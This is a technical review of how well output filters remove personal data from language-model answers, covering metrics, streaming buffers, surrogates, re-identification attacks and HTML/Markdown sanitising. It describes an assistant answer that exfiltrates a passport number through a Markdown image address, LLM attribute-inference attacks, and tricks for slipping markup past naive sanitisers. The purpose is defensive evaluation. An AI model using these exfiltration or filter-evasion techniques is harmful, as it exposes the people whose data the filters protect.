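The main score is a weighted average of the F1 for each type. Leakage density, which the researchers call SPriv, is the measure Garza and colleagues used for masked texts.

```
risk-weighted F1 = sum of (weight × F1) over the 11 types / sum of the weights
leakage density  = sensitive tokens left in the output / all tokens in the output
```

The weights add up to 4 × 1 + 5 × 3 + 2 × 9 = 37. Card and social security numbers account for 18 of the 37, almost half of the score.

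*Safer Reasoning Traces* describes recall in two opposite ways. The formula in its method section gives the share of sensitive tokens in the prompt that leaked, so a high value is bad. The tables of filter results give the share of leaks that a filter blocked, so a high value is good. All the recall figures for filters below use the second definition. The leakage rates of 52.3% and 86.3% are closer to the first, although they count runs instead of tokens. Counting runs makes little difference in practice because a model that leaked an item always leaked all of it.

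| Filter | Published recall | Leaks missed | Recall from the counts | Risk-weighted F1 | Leakage density |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Rules | 0.414 | 3,468 | 0.39 | 0.632 | 0.0248 |
| Word statistics | 0.321 | 3,768 | 0.34 | 0.310 | 0.0117 |
| GLiNER2 | 0.560 | 161 | 0.97 | 0.841 | 0.0010 |
| Judge, o4-mini | 0.492 | 2,926 | 0.49 | 0.682 | 0.0201 |
| Judge, Claude Opus | 0.848 | 556 | 0.90 | 0.741 | 0.0023 |

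Leakage density depends heavily on response length. The rules missed 614 leaks from Mixtral and 565 from DeepSeek-R1, but the density was 0.0458 for Mixtral and only 0.0109 for DeepSeek-R1. DeepSeek-R1's responses were more than five times as long in the researchers' baseline runs, so each leak adds less to its density, even though a reader can use a leaked card number just as easily when it appears in a long response.

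### Why the judge with the best recall came second

The Claude Opus judge has the highest published recall, 0.848, but GLiNER2 has the highest risk-weighted F1, 0.841 compared with 0.741 for the judge. Ahrend and colleagues explain that the judge catches more leaks overall but misses some of the most sensitive ones.

The judge missed 115 of the 410 social security numbers, including all 24 from o3 and all 50 from DeepSeek-R1. GLiNER2 missed none of them, and none of the 251 card numbers. A type with a weight of 9 makes up 24% of the score, so a judge that misses every social security number loses that 24% even if it finds every name.

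GLiNER2 missed 161 leaks and the judge missed 556, so the counts don't support the claim that the judge catches more overall. For five of the six models, GLiNER2's published recall is half the value calculated from the counts, which looks like an averaging mistake. For example, it blocked 1,075 of Llama's 1,090 leaks, a recall of 0.986, but the summary lists 0.493. Averaged in the same way as the judge's recall of 0.848, GLiNER2's would be about 0.957.

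Of GLiNER2's 161 misses, 99 were MAC addresses and 54 were IP addresses. The rules caught every MAC address, so adding the MAC address rule to GLiNER2 would have reduced its misses to at most 62 of the 5,697 leaks. This is a strong argument for the hybrid filters described earlier.

The judge's prompt may also have limited its performance. The prompt listed the types of data to look for but left out phone numbers, and the judge missed 102 of the 493 phone numbers that leaked.

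### The low scores on DeepSeek-R1

All five filters scored well below their best on DeepSeek-R1.

| Filter | Risk-weighted F1 on DeepSeek-R1 | Average over six models |
|---|---|---|
| Rules | 0.637 | 0.632 |
| GLiNER2 | 0.619 | 0.841 |
| Judge, o4-mini | 0.393 | 0.682 |
| Judge, Claude Opus | 0.256 | 0.741 |
| Word statistics | 0.118 | 0.310 |

Ahrend and colleagues suggest that DeepSeek-R1's long reasoning changes personal data into forms the filters don't recognise. This is hard to reconcile with their method, which counted a leak only when the whole item appeared, and with the fact that GLiNER2 blocked 828 of DeepSeek-R1's 847 leaks.

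GLiNER2 produced many false alarms. DeepSeek-R1 repeated a card number in one of 100 runs. GLiNER2 caught it, but its F1 for card numbers was 0.020, which means that it also flagged about 98 responses without a leaked card number. Half of the runs leaked a social security number, but GLiNER2 flagged all 100. The responses may have discussed such numbers or given wrong ones, but the counts are not enough to determine what triggered the flags.

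The Claude Opus judge missed all 242 IP addresses, MAC addresses and social security numbers that DeepSeek-R1 leaked. The rules did about as well on DeepSeek-R1's outputs as they did on average.

The rules came first only because of the single card number. They caught it without a false alarm, for an F1 of 1 on a type with a weight of 9. The F1 scores added up within each risk group give

```
           mild        medium       high
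Rules      1 × 0     + 3 × 3.618 + 9 × 1.413 = 23.57    23.57 / 37 = 0.637
GLiNER2    1 × 4     + 3 × 4.241 + 9 × 0.687 = 22.91    22.91 / 37 = 0.619
```

Without card numbers, the rules would score 0.52 and GLiNER2 0.81. A similar distortion affects the scores on Claude Opus's responses, which contained no card numbers. The calculation still gives every filter an F1 of 0 for that type, so even a perfect filter could score at most 28/37, or 0.76.

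The ranking of GLiNER2 above the rules and the small judge is probably sound, because GLiNER2 missed far fewer leaks. The exact figures will not carry over to a product. The researchers told GLiNER2 and the judges which type to look for in each response, but a filter in a product has to look for all types at once. The prompts were short, in English, and not designed to get around the filters. The judges are also much weaker than current models, so a newer judge might well miss fewer leaks.

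### Filtering text as it arrives

Ahrend and colleagues' filters read complete responses. In a chat interface, text usually arrives in chunks, and an identifier can begin in one chunk and end in the next, so a filter there has to hold back any text that could be the start of an identifier.

Suppose a filter looks only for three digits followed by a hyphen and four digits, and the travel agency's assistant writes "Call back on 555-0142 or write" in five chunks.

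| New chunk | Held back | Released |
|---|---|---|
| "Call back on " | – | "Call back on " |
| "555" | "555" | – |
| "-01" | "555-01" | – |
| "42" | "555-0142" | – |
| " or write" | – | "[PHONE] or write" |

After the fourth chunk, the filter has a complete phone number but waits, because another digit would make it a longer number of a different type. If the model stops there, the filter treats the held text as complete and masks it.

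Some filters collect a fixed amount of text before each scan. If a filter scanned and released 50 characters at a time, a card number written with spaces (19 characters) would cross a boundary whenever it began in the last 18 positions, or 36% of the time. The filter can prevent this by holding back the last 18 characters of each chunk and scanning them again with the next. Names and postal addresses have no fixed length, so any fixed holdback will occasionally split one.

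Trained detectors such as Privacy Filter may also need the words that follow an identifier, so a filter that uses one has to hold back more text.

To block the Markdown image in the agency's example, the filter also has to hold back everything from the exclamation mark to the closing parenthesis. An attacker can make the image's address longer than the buffer, so a filter that reaches its limit should delete the held text instead of releasing it.

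Amazon Bedrock, a service for running language models, lets customers trade speed against safety in its filters, which it calls guardrails. According to AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content*, the default synchronous mode holds one or more chunks of the response until the scan finishes, which adds some delay but improves accuracy. The default interval between scans is 50 characters, according to AWS's draft reference page *StreamingConfigurations* (2026), so a response of 1,500 characters needs about 30 scans. A larger interval means fewer scans. AWS also offers an asynchronous mode, in which Bedrock sends text before the scan finishes.

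LiteLLM connects applications to many model providers. By default, it withholds the whole response until one scan has passed and then shows it to the user all at once, according to LiteLLM's *Bedrock Guardrails*. Developers can let the text through while the scan runs, but then the filter can only record a leak that the user has already seen. Bifrost, a similar product, also checks the complete response rather than separate chunks.

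Kong's *AI AWS Guardrails Policy* lets developers set the buffer size in tokens and uses 50 as an example. A smaller buffer catches problems sooner but needs more scans. By default, the policy checks only the user's input, so a company that wants output filtering has to turn it on.

A filter adds delay because it waits for text and then scans it. If a model writes 50 tokens a second, a 50-token buffer delays the first words by one second, and holding a 300-token response until it is complete delays them by six. In the surrogate study described below, Privacy Filter scanned 512 tokens in about one second on an ordinary processor, so scanning the 300-token response would add roughly 0.6 seconds.

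### What removal costs the answer

A filter that removes everything it finds may also remove what the user asked for. Two studies tested whether software can tell which personal details are needed to answer a question. Both masked details in the user's text before a model read it, so the loss they measured differs from the loss an output filter causes.

*CAPID* (Ponomarenko, Abedini and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a warehouse supervisor with chronic back pain who asks how to feel less tired after long shifts. The job and the illness matter for the advice, but a filter can mask the supervisor's town and two children without making the advice worse.

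The researchers generated 2,307 texts of this kind with language models. Five annotators corrected the labels, marking a detail as relevant only if the question was impossible or very hard to answer without it. Health details were relevant in 56% of cases, occupations in 52%, locations in 48% and ages in 26%. Names were relevant in 1%, and codes such as ID numbers never were.

After training on these texts, a small Llama model correctly judged the relevance of 80% of the details it found in 150 real Reddit posts, compared with 69% for GPT-4.1-mini. The researchers then had GPT-4 answer each question twice, once with all personal details masked and once with only the irrelevant ones masked. As judges, GPT-4 preferred the answer from the lightly masked text in 80% of cases and Claude Sonnet 4.5 in 79%. On the invented texts, the figures were 79% and 73%. The judges saw the original text and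 had to choose the answer it supported better, which favours answers that mention more details. The percentages also don't show how much better the preferred answers were.

In *PII-Bench*, Shen, Gu and colleagues (2025) measured how much utility is lost through masking. They masked 200 descriptions of people in different ways and had GPT-4o answer questions about them. The utility score combines a model's rating of each answer with that answer's similarity to the one from the unmasked text.

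| Masking | Share of personal details hidden | Utility |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 1.00 |
| Everything | 100% | 0.52 |
| Only details the question doesn't need | 83% | 0.89 |

The last row probably shows what perfect judgement would achieve, because the researchers hid about 83% of the details, the same share that the correct labels mark as unnecessary across the whole benchmark. On descriptions of one person, GPT-4o identified the necessary details with an F1 of 0.63 using a plain prompt and 0.72 using the best prompting method, while people reached 0.95. GPT-4o reached 0.84 when it had a list of the details to choose from. Shen and colleagues consider such a list unrealistic, but a filter with a separate detector has one, although it will contain some errors. Models' accuracy fell sharply when a text described more than five people.

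The drop in utility to 0.52 doesn't apply to output filters. When "[OCCUPATION]" replaces the job in the input, the model has to give advice without knowing the job. An output filter acts after the model has used the job to work out its answer, so the advice can still be good even if the filter hides the word "supervisor". The reader is worse off only if the filter hides something they needed to read.

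The idea of judging relevance does carry over. If the agency's employee asks how to reach the customer, the filter should keep the name and phone number and remove the passport number, which it can do only if it takes the question as well as the answer as input. CAPID's figures for each type would be a poor guide here, because names hardly matter in requests for advice but are often the answer to a question about a customer file.

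A detail can also be relevant even when the person asking shouldn't see it. For example, a stranger who asks for Marta Lindqvist's phone number shouldn't get it. The details that CAPID most often keeps, such as health, job and location, are also quasi-identifiers, so keeping them reduces privacy.

### Surrogates

For stored text, surrogates are an alternative to masks such as AWS's "[NAME-1]". *Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution*, from May 2026, is the fullest test of surrogates. The researchers used Privacy Filter to find personal data in 100 invented documents, such as invoices and bank statements, from six countries or regions. They compared ordinary masks with two kinds of surrogate. One came entirely from Faker, a program that generates random values by rule. The other used Faker for phone numbers and similar items,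 and a small language model for names, addresses and dates.

| Method | Real values still present | Time per document |
|---|---|---|
| Masks | 24.9% | 1.7 seconds |
| Faker | 24.9% | 1.6 seconds |
| Faker and a language model | 24.9% | 41.2 seconds |

The leakage is the same in all three rows because the detector missed the same values each time, and the filter can replace only the values that the detector finds. By the researchers' measure, the language model made the text more natural, but it took about 24 times as long on a computer without a graphics card.

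The researchers first gave the filter three fixed examples, each pairing a real value with its replacement. It often copied a replacement from the examples, so a Chinese, a Japanese and a German name all became "Alice Johnson". They fixed this by choosing examples in the same language as the input and varying them from one input to the next. Some Japanese names still became Chinese ones, because the program that identified the language couldn't tell Japanese from Chinese names.

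The researchers also trained a detector on the altered documents and tested it on originals. Its F1 was 0 when the training texts were masked, presumably because they contained no real-looking names or numbers. It reached 0.656 with Faker's values and 0.960 with the original data. In a smaller comparison, Faker's values gave 0.506 and the language model's gave 0.346. The language model drew on a narrow range of names, and variety helped the detector more than natural wording did. Faker is therefore both faster and better than the language model for logs that will serve as training data.

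Surrogates may also hide identifiers that the detector missed, an effect found in work on medical records and known as "hiding in plain sight". If a filter masks 95 of 100 names, a reader can tell that the remaining five are real, but if it replaces the 95 with plausible invented names, the reader can't tell which five are real. The documents in the May 2026 study contained about 6.6 personal values each, so on average between one and two real values would remain among five invented ones.

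This protection depends on convincing surrogates. If every replaced name on a Chinese insurance form becomes "Alice Johnson", the one Chinese name left is obviously real. If the filter replaces a name but misses a later mention of it, that mention can also reveal the real name. Surrogates offer little protection against a neighbour who already knows the name, or against someone who can test the values, since a real phone number still works when dialled. The 24.9% leakage figure is based on exact matches in the text, so it doesn't measure whether readers would have picked out the real values.

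### Filters that block exact copies

Before detectors like these were common, researchers tried to stop models from reproducing their training text. An exact-copy filter compares the model's output with that text and blocks any long sequence of words that appears in both, so it doesn't need a definition of personal data.

Ippolito and colleagues showed in 2022 that a filter that blocks exact copies still lets near-copies through. If the model changes a few words, the spelling or the punctuation, the filter finds no match, but a reader learns the same thing. With personal data, changing one character can be enough, since "555 0142" reaches the same person as "555-0142".

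In newer work on memorisation by Luo and colleagues, models completed real email addresses that they had not seen in training. An exact-copy filter would miss these addresses because it only compares outputs with the training data. It would miss data from conversations, retrieved documents and tool results for the same reason.

Exact comparison is still useful when the company knows which values to protect. The travel agency's system has just fetched Lindqvist's record, so a filter could look for her passport number in the answer without recognising passport numbers in general. It would need to ignore spaces, hyphens and capitalisation, and check for encoded forms such as the one in the example's image address.

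## Measuring the personal data that remains after filtering

Every filter described so far leaves some personal data in the text, and the measured amount depends on what one counts. Suppose the travel agency's log holds a conversation about Marta Lindqvist, and the filter masks four of the five mentions of her name. The filter has removed 80% of the mentions, but it has not protected her, because anyone who opens the log can still read her name.

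### Missed tokens and spans

The most lenient measure counts the tokens or spans that the detector missed. Leakage density and most of the recall figures in earlier sections are of this kind. These figures make it easy to compare detectors and find the types of data each handles badly. They are a poor measure of any one person's exposure, because they count every missed mention of a name equally.

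Scores also depend on what the annotators labelled. In *DialogPII*, Roller, Czehmann and colleagues (2026) present invented conversations in 11 languages, including emergency calls, police reports and therapy sessions. Their labels cover professions and ages, so a filter that left "harbour pilot" or "58" in place would lose points. However, they labelled indirect identifiers only in part, because annotators find it hard to mark these consistently, and they state that the labels are not meant to guarantee complete anonymisation. A filter could therefore find every labelled item and still leave someone recognisable.

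### Masking every mention

A stricter measure counts an identifier as removed only if the filter masks every mention of it. *The Text Anonymization Benchmark (TAB)* (Pilán, Lison and colleagues, 2022) applies this rule to judgments of the European Court of Human Rights. Law students marked the details that could identify the applicant, the person who brought the case. They also linked different forms of the same name, such as "John Doe" and "Mr Doe", so that they count as one entity.

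```
protected(e)  = 1 if the filter masks every mention of entity e completely, otherwise 0
entity recall = sum of protected(e) over all entities / number of entities
```

"The Text Anonymization Benchmark" calculates entity recall separately for direct identifiers, such as names and case numbers, and for quasi-identifiers, such as dates and places. Of the 155,006 mentions in its collection, 4.4% are direct identifiers and 63.4% are quasi-identifiers. A single figure for both would mostly reflect the quasi-identifiers and could hide a failure to remove names.

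Annotators may reasonably choose different details to mask, so the measure includes every annotator's choices. In the researchers' example, a British researcher called John Doe brings a case against Sweden. Both annotators mark the name and the case number as direct identifiers. For quasi-identifiers, the first marks the date and "British", and the second marks the date, "Kingdom of Sweden" and "researcher". Presidio masks the name, the date and the country:

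```
Direct identifiers   (1 + 1) / (2 + 2) = 0.5
Quasi-identifiers    (1 + 2) / (2 + 3) = 0.6
```

The table shows the results for three systems on the benchmark's test judgments. The general detector is a named-entity recognition model without special training for this task. The researchers trained Longformer, a token classifier for long texts, on other judgments from the collection.

| System | Token recall | Entity recall, direct | Entity recall, quasi | Token precision |
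|---|---|---|---|---|
| Presidio | 0.707 | 0.460 | 0.758 | 0.761 |
| General detector | 0.906 | 0.940 | 0.874 | 0.441 |
| Longformer | 0.919 | 1.000 | 0.916 | 0.836 |

Presidio left more than half of the direct identifiers readable, even though its token recall looks acceptable. This was mainly because it had no recogniser for court case numbers and missed all of them. Anyone can look up a case number to find the applicant. The general detector happened to catch these numbers because the researchers had set it to mask any number of four or more digits. It would have missed case numbers that contained letters.

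Entity recall can also be higher than token recall, as it is for Presidio's quasi-identifiers. Entity recall counts an entity once even if it appears 20 times, so missing a few frequent or long entities lowers token recall more than entity recall. A company can't calculate one figure from the other.

When training Longformer, the researchers treated a miss as ten times as serious as a false alarm. On the court judgments they used for development, this raised entity recall for quasi-identifiers from 0.847 to 0.936 and lowered precision from 0.925 to 0.795. The model's entity recall was also high on Wikipedia biographies, at 0.999 for direct identifiers and 0.923 for quasi-identifiers.

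If a detector's misses were independent, the chance of removing an identifier completely would fall quickly with the number of mentions:

| Recall per mention | 1 mention | 2 mentions | 4 mentions | 8 mentions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.98 | 98% | 96% | 92% | 85% |
| 0.95 | 95% | 90% | 81% | 66% |
| 0.90 | 90% | 81% | 66% | 43% |

In practice, a detector's misses are rarely independent. A detector that recognises "Marta Lindqvist" once will usually recognise it again in a similar sentence, but it is more likely to miss a mention that looks different, such as a first name in lower case. A filter can catch some of these mentions by searching the whole text for every name it has already found. This search misses nicknames and misspellings, and it may also mask the month of May if a customer has that name.

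### Long conversations

Personal data is harder to remove completely from conversations because the clue to a word's meaning can be many messages away. Zhang and colleagues (2026) built a detector, PII-Tracer, for this setting. According to Hsu and Berlin, Zhang's team used leading language models to label multilingual conversations with assistants, and PII-Tracer tags tokens in the same way as Privacy Filter.

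A detector of this design can process only a limited amount of text at once. Perplexity's *pplx-pii-masking*, a model for masking personal data in conversations, has about 600 million parameters and nine categories, and accepts up to 4,096 tokens. A program has to split a longer conversation into windows and scan each one. If the user writes "my sister is called Robin" at the end of one window and "Robin hates flying" at the start of the next, the model processes the second sentence without the first.

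Overlapping windows reduce this problem. If each window starts 2,048 tokens after the previous one starts, every token away from the ends of the conversation falls into two windows and has at least 1,024 tokens of context on each side in at least one of them. The program can mask whatever either scan finds. This takes about twice the computation and keeps the false alarms from both scans. Overlap doesn't help when a clue is 10,000 tokens away. For that, the filter needs a list of names it has already found.

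Longer context windows can improve precision without improving recall. When Pilán and colleagues gave Longformer windows of 32 tokens, its entity recall for quasi-identifiers was 0.952, compared with 0.936 at 4,096 tokens. Precision was 0.470 with the short windows and 0.795 with the long ones. With little context, the model apparently masked anything that might be personal. The test documents were court judgments, which use full names and capitals. Context may matter more for recall in chats, which often lack these cues.

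A company that tests its filter only on short chats, or on the opening of long ones, will probably underestimate how much personal data gets through. *Chatbot Confessions*, by Mollaeefar, Van Landuyt and colleagues, analysed only the users' messages in 100,342 conversations with ChatGPT, Copilot and Gemini that users had shared through public links. In longer conversations, 60% of the private disclosures came in the last quarter. Conversations of more than 15,000 characters were 2.5 times as likely to pose a privacy risk as short ones. In English, 15,000 characters is roughly 3,750 tokens, not counting the chatbot's answers, so a window of 4,096 tokens would rarely hold the whole exchange.

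### People who can be recognised without a name

The strictest measure is whether someone can still identify the person the text is about, or learn facts about that person that the filter should have hidden. Lindqvist's job, town and age may still fit only one person after the filter has masked all four of her identifiers. In privacy statistics, k is the number of people who fit a description. A common rule for releasing tables of personal data sets a minimum for k.

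A few details can be enough to bring k down to one. *Early Detection of Re-Identification Risk in Multi-Turn Dialogues* (Lee, Park and Son, 2026) summarises older research which found that sex, date of birth and postcode together single out between 63% and 87% of the US population. It also reports that four credit card purchases single out 90% of shoppers in a set of transactions, and that one group estimated 15 demographic attributes would single out 99.98% of adults.

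These studies used tables and location records rather than chats. Even when a description fits only one person, an attacker who wants to identify that person needs another source that contains both the details and the name, such as a staff page that lists the harbour pilots. The risk from the remaining details therefore depends on what the reader already knows or can look up.

### Language models as attackers

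Staab and colleagues (2024) showed that language models can infer personal attributes from what people write, even if the models have never seen anything about the writers. In later work, they found that 66.3% of attributes could still be inferred after a named-entity recognition filter had masked the text (cited in Oh, Kim and colleagues, 2026, *Subject-level Inference for Realistic Text Anonymization Evaluation*).

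Staab and colleagues' attack targets one person per text, usually the author. Oh and colleagues extended it to everyone a text mentions. They used 144 court judgments from the Text Anonymization Benchmark and 151 invented online texts. Human annotators had listed what a reader could learn about each person in 15 categories, including passport number, name, sex, age, nationality and occupation.

The researchers filtered the texts in four ways:

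- Longformer, the model trained on court judgments, masked the spans it found.
- DeID-GPT instructed a language model to find listed types of personal data and redact them.
- DP-Prompt had a language model paraphrase the text with a high degree of randomness, to hide the author's style.
- Adversarial anonymisation had one language model guess facts about a chosen person and then removed the clues it had used, in several rounds.

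Claude Sonnet 4.5 acted as the attacker. It read only the filtered text, identified the people in it, and inferred the facts about each person. A correct inference scored 1, a partly correct one 0.5, and a wrong one 0. For example, "California" scored 0.5 if the right answer was Los Angeles.

Oh and colleagues calculated protection in two ways. For each person, O is the number of facts in the original text, and A is the attacker's score on the filtered text.

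```
collective protection = 1 − (sum of A over all people) / (sum of O over all people)
individual protection = average of (1 − A / O) over all people
```

Suppose a text contains eight facts about Lindqvist and two about a ferry clerk, and the attacker correctly infers two facts about each. Collective protection is 1 − 4/10, or 0.60. Individual protection is the average of 0.75 for Lindqvist and 0 for the clerk, or 0.375. A filter that protects the main person but not the others therefore scores lower on the individual measure.

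The table gives token recall and collective protection. GPT-4.1 was the language model behind the last three methods.

| Method | Judgments: recall | Judgments: protection | Online texts: recall | Online texts: protection |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Longformer | 0.940 | 0.330 | 0.883 | 0.597 |
| DeID-GPT | 0.990 | 0.674 | 0.984 | 0.799 |
| DP-Prompt | 0.561 | 0.137 | 0.208 | 0.130 |
| Adversarial anonymisation | 0.894 | 0.359 | 0.969 | 0.870 |

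In the judgments, Longformer masked 94% of the labelled tokens and removed every mention of 99.7% of the direct identifiers, but the attacker still scored 67% of the available points. Protection was lower than token recall for every method in the table, and the gap was larger in the judgments than in the online texts. The judgments average 3,918 characters and the online texts 260, so the attacker had far more context in the judgments.

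The last few quasi-identifiers seem to matter most. Oh and colleagues ran DeID-GPT with six language models, and all six removed every direct identifier from the judgments. Their results differed widely all the same, as these four show:

| Model behind DeID-GPT | Quasi-identifiers fully masked | Collective protection | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 89.5% | 0.396 | 0.961 |
| GPT-4.1 Mini | 95.6% | 0.430 | 0.959 |
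| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 97.4% | 0.570 | 0.947 |
| GPT-4.1 | 99.1% | 0.674 | 0.754 |

The utility score combines ratings of readability and preserved meaning with a measure of overlap with the original text. Between the first and last rows, the share of fully masked quasi-identifiers rose by about 10 percentage points and protection rose by 28. One explanation is that an attacker can infer a masked detail from those that remain, such as a town from the name of a court. GPT-4.1 probably also removed text that the annotators had not labelled, which would explain the sharp drop in utility. Claude Haiku 4.5 achieved a good part of the gain in protection with little loss of utility.

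### How to read a protection score of 0.33

This score gives a person's sex the same weight as their name, and a single "he" can reveal a person's sex, so the score doesn't mean that the attacker could name two-thirds of the people. Oh and colleagues acknowledge that equal weights are a limitation, because very different risks can produce the same score. They also note that the score doesn't measure how facts combine to single someone out.

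Longformer was trained to protect only the applicant, while the judgments mention four people on average. This seems to explain little of its low score, because its protection for applicants alone was 0.384, only slightly better than the 0.330 for everyone.

Another possible explanation is that Claude saw some of the judgments, which are public, during training and recalled facts that the filtered text no longer supports. The online texts are invented, so they don't have this problem, and Longformer's protection on them was 0.597. The experiment can't separate the effect of memory from that of length.

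The ranking of methods is more reliable than their scores. When the researchers replaced the attacker with GPT-4.1 or Claude Haiku 4.5, the methods stayed in almost the same order, with a rank correlation above 0.98. But all three attackers are well behind current models, which would probably infer more personal data.

Adversarial anonymisation did best on the online texts but badly on the judgments, where it protected the applicant better than other people. With Claude Sonnet 4.5 as the filter's model, protection was 0.472 for the applicant and 0.362 for everyone. In the online texts, the changes also protected people other than the author. For example, changing "Married life with Lisa" to "Life with others" hides Lisa as well as the author's marriage. A travel agency that wants to protect everyone in its logs can't assume that a method designed to protect one customer will also protect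 the customer's family.

### Details that add up over a conversation

People often reveal personal details gradually in a chat. Lee and colleagues give the example of a customer with a late parcel who first mentions downtown San Francisco, then an office on Market Street, then a reception desk. A filter that checks each message separately would flag none of them.

The system keeps a separate record of details about the user and each other person mentioned. It raises one warning when one person's quasi-identifiers reach a set score, and another when a name appears with a direct identifier such as a phone number. To reduce errors, it records a detail only once there is enough evidence for it.

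The researchers tested the system on 184 conversations they generated from templates. On average, its warning came 2.4 turns from the correct turn, compared with 5.5 for a simpler version that added up every detail it found. The correct turn was the one at which the researchers' own rule should have fired, so the test measures how well the system follows that rule, and nobody tried to identify the speakers.

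The experiments also assume different attackers. Lee and colleagues assume a reader who sees the whole conversation and knows general facts, such as which city a university is in, but doesn't look anyone up. The annotators of the Text Anonymization Benchmark had to consider anything an attacker could find in public, including on the web. Oh and colleagues' attacker had the filtered text and whatever it had learned in training. A neighbour, colleague or former spouse of Marta Lindqvist has private knowledge that none of these tests includes, so a filter's results in them are weak evidence of how well it protects against such readers.

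### From recall to the share of leaking documents

A filter with high recall can still leave personal data in many documents. If each document contains eight different identifiers, the filter finds each with a probability of 0.98, and its misses are independent, then about 15% of documents will still contain at least one identifier after filtering.

```
chance that all eight are removed        0.98^8     = 0.851
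chance that at least one remains         1 − 0.851  = 0.149
```

About 15% of the documents still contain at least one identifier after filtering, or roughly 1,500 in a log of 10,000. The filter would need a recall of about 0.9987 to bring this share below 1%.

The assumed recall of 0.98 is probably too high for complete identifiers in a company's own documents. OpenAI's Privacy Filter reached 0.98 on PII-Masking-300k, but that recall was measured per token on synthetic text.

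Misses also tend to cluster. If a transcript is all in lower case, the filter may miss every name in it. With a recall of 0.98 and eight identifiers per document, an average of 0.16 identifiers remain in each document, however the misses are distributed. If the filter either finds all eight or misses all eight, only 2% of documents leak, but each of those exposes all eight identifiers. If no document has more than one miss, 16% leak. The figure of 15% is therefore close to the worst case for the number of affected documents, but clustered misses expose more about the people in each one.

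### What a clean sample proves

A company can also read a random sample of filtered outputs and count the leaks. Suppose that it checks 3,000 outputs and finds none. The true leak rate may still be above zero, because a rare leak can easily be absent from the sample. If the rate is p, the chance of finding no leaks in 3,000 outputs is (1 − p)^3000. Setting this chance to 5% gives the highest rate that the sample doesn't rule out at 95% confidence:

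```
(1 − p)^3000 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/3000) = 0.000998, or about 0.1%
```

A common shortcut is to divide 3 by the size of the sample. To show that the rate is below 0.01%, the company would have to check about 30,000 outputs without finding a leak. Each leak it does find raises the upper bound:

| Leaks found in 3,000 outputs | Upper bound on the leak rate |
|---|---|
| 0 | 0.10% |
| 1 | 0.16% |
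| 3 | 0.26% |
| 5 | 0.35% |

A leak rate of 0.1% would mean up to 1,000 leaking answers in every million. It may also be a poor measure of how well the filter works. If only 0.5% of a chatbot's answers contain an identifier before filtering, a sample of 3,000 includes about 15 such answers. A filter that misses one in ten would still catch all 15 about a fifth of the time (0.9^15 = 0.21). To test the filter, the company needs a sample of answers that contained identifiers before filtering, and it has to find them without relying on the filter.

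The bound holds only if the sample is random and covers the traffic that the company cares about. A sample from March doesn't cover a feature launched in April. Choosing the riskiest conversations, for instance with the sensitivity score that Perplexity's model gives each one, is a good way to find leaks, but the share of leaks among them isn't the leak rate for all conversations. The outputs should also come from separate conversations, since 3,000 answers from 50 long chats give much less information than 3,000 from different users.

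The calculation also assumes that the reviewers notice every leak. If they notice only 80% of leaks, the upper bound rises from 0.1% to about 0.125%, and if they notice only half, it rises to 0.2%.

### Checking with something other than the filter

Running the filter's own detector again on a sample is the easiest check, but it proves little because the detector will mostly miss what it missed the first time. Suppose a filter has removed 900 of 1,000 phone numbers and left 100 in an unfamiliar format. A second run finds none of the 100, and the company records a leak rate of zero. The check can still reveal technical faults, such as text that bypassed the filter.

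A second detector helps if it fails on different things, as the rules and GLiNER2 did in Ahrend and colleagues' experiment. Two detectors also make it possible to estimate how much both have missed. Run both on the original text, remove the false alarms by hand, and calculate

```
estimated total = (found by A × found by B) / found by both
```

If detector A finds 900 identifiers, detector B finds 800, and 720 of these are the same, the estimated total is 1,000. A has missed about 100, of which B has found 80. The estimate is correct only if the two detectors miss things independently. If both tend to miss the same lower-case names, their findings will overlap more. With 780 findings in common, the estimated total is only 923, and A appears to have missed 23 identifiers when it may have missed 100. A set of rules and a language model are therefore a better pair than two models trained on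 the same data.

Mollaeefar and colleagues first used regular expressions to mark items with a fixed format, then used a language model to find details that depend on context, such as an illness or an employer. They measured an accuracy of 77.5% against the judgements of expert annotators, so their finding that 8% of the shared conversations pose a privacy risk is an estimate with a substantial margin of error. They also point out that WildChat, a collection of real chats, still contained many private disclosures after its publishers had redacted it with named-entity recognition. Other researchers found these disclosures by looking at context.

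Human reviewers can notice personal data that no detector has a category for, such as a job that only one person in town holds. Annotators for the Text Anonymization Benchmark received court judgments in which a detector and some extra rules had already marked likely items. Pilán and colleagues report that the annotators themselves added 18% of the final mentions.

Human reviewers also miss personal data, and they disagree with each other. When the annotators classified items as direct identifiers, quasi-identifiers or harmless, their agreement on exact spans, corrected for chance, was only 0.46, where 1 is perfect. Some of this disagreement is legitimate, because different sets of masks can protect the same person. A company can have two people review part of the sample separately, without seeing the filter's marks, and compare what they find. It also has to limit who takes part, since each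 reviewer sees the personal data the filter missed.

Planted test identifiers let a tester measure how often a filter misses identifiers that are rare in ordinary answers. The tester puts invented names, passport numbers and phone numbers into customer records, emails or prompts, then runs the whole system. Because the tester knows every planted value, a simple search of the screen output and the log shows which ones got through. Ahrend and colleagues' experiment worked on this principle. If 500 planted passport numbers reach the filter and none gets past it, the miss rate for passport numbers like these is below about 0.6% at 95% confidence. A random sample of ordinary answers would have to be very large to contain 500 passport numbers.

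The tester has to count only the planted values that the model tried to repeat, which requires a copy of the unfiltered output. Otherwise, values that the model ignored would make the filter look better than it is. The values should be unique, so that a match can't be a coincidence, and they must not belong to a real person. Published test card numbers can give misleading results, because a filter may have an exception for them.

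Tests with planted values cover only the types and formats of personal data that the tester thought of. A test with 500 passport numbers in the same format does not measure whether the filter removes nicknames or job titles. Neither a filter that matches surface text nor a search for exact planted values can recognise every way of rewording a fact, so testers need to read some of the outputs in which the search found nothing.

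## Removing unsafe HTML and Markdown: methods and laboratory tests

The travel agency's example answer ends with an image whose address contains Marta Lindqvist's encoded passport number. The part of the filter that handles markup only has to stop the browser from running code or contacting a server that the agency hasn't approved, so it doesn't need to decode the address.

### Why deleting bad strings fails

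The simplest method is a regular expression that deletes dangerous strings, such as every `<script` and `<img`. This works badly because the same instruction can take many forms. Klein and Johns pointed out in *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* (2024) that browsers must treat a tag named `image` as `img`, so a pattern for `<img` would miss it. Markdown also lets a writer put an image's address on a separate line from the image.

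Deleting a string can create a new copy of it. For example, deleting "img" from "iimgmg" leaves "img". Browsers also repair faulty HTML instead of rejecting it, so a broken tag that matches none of a filter's patterns may still work.

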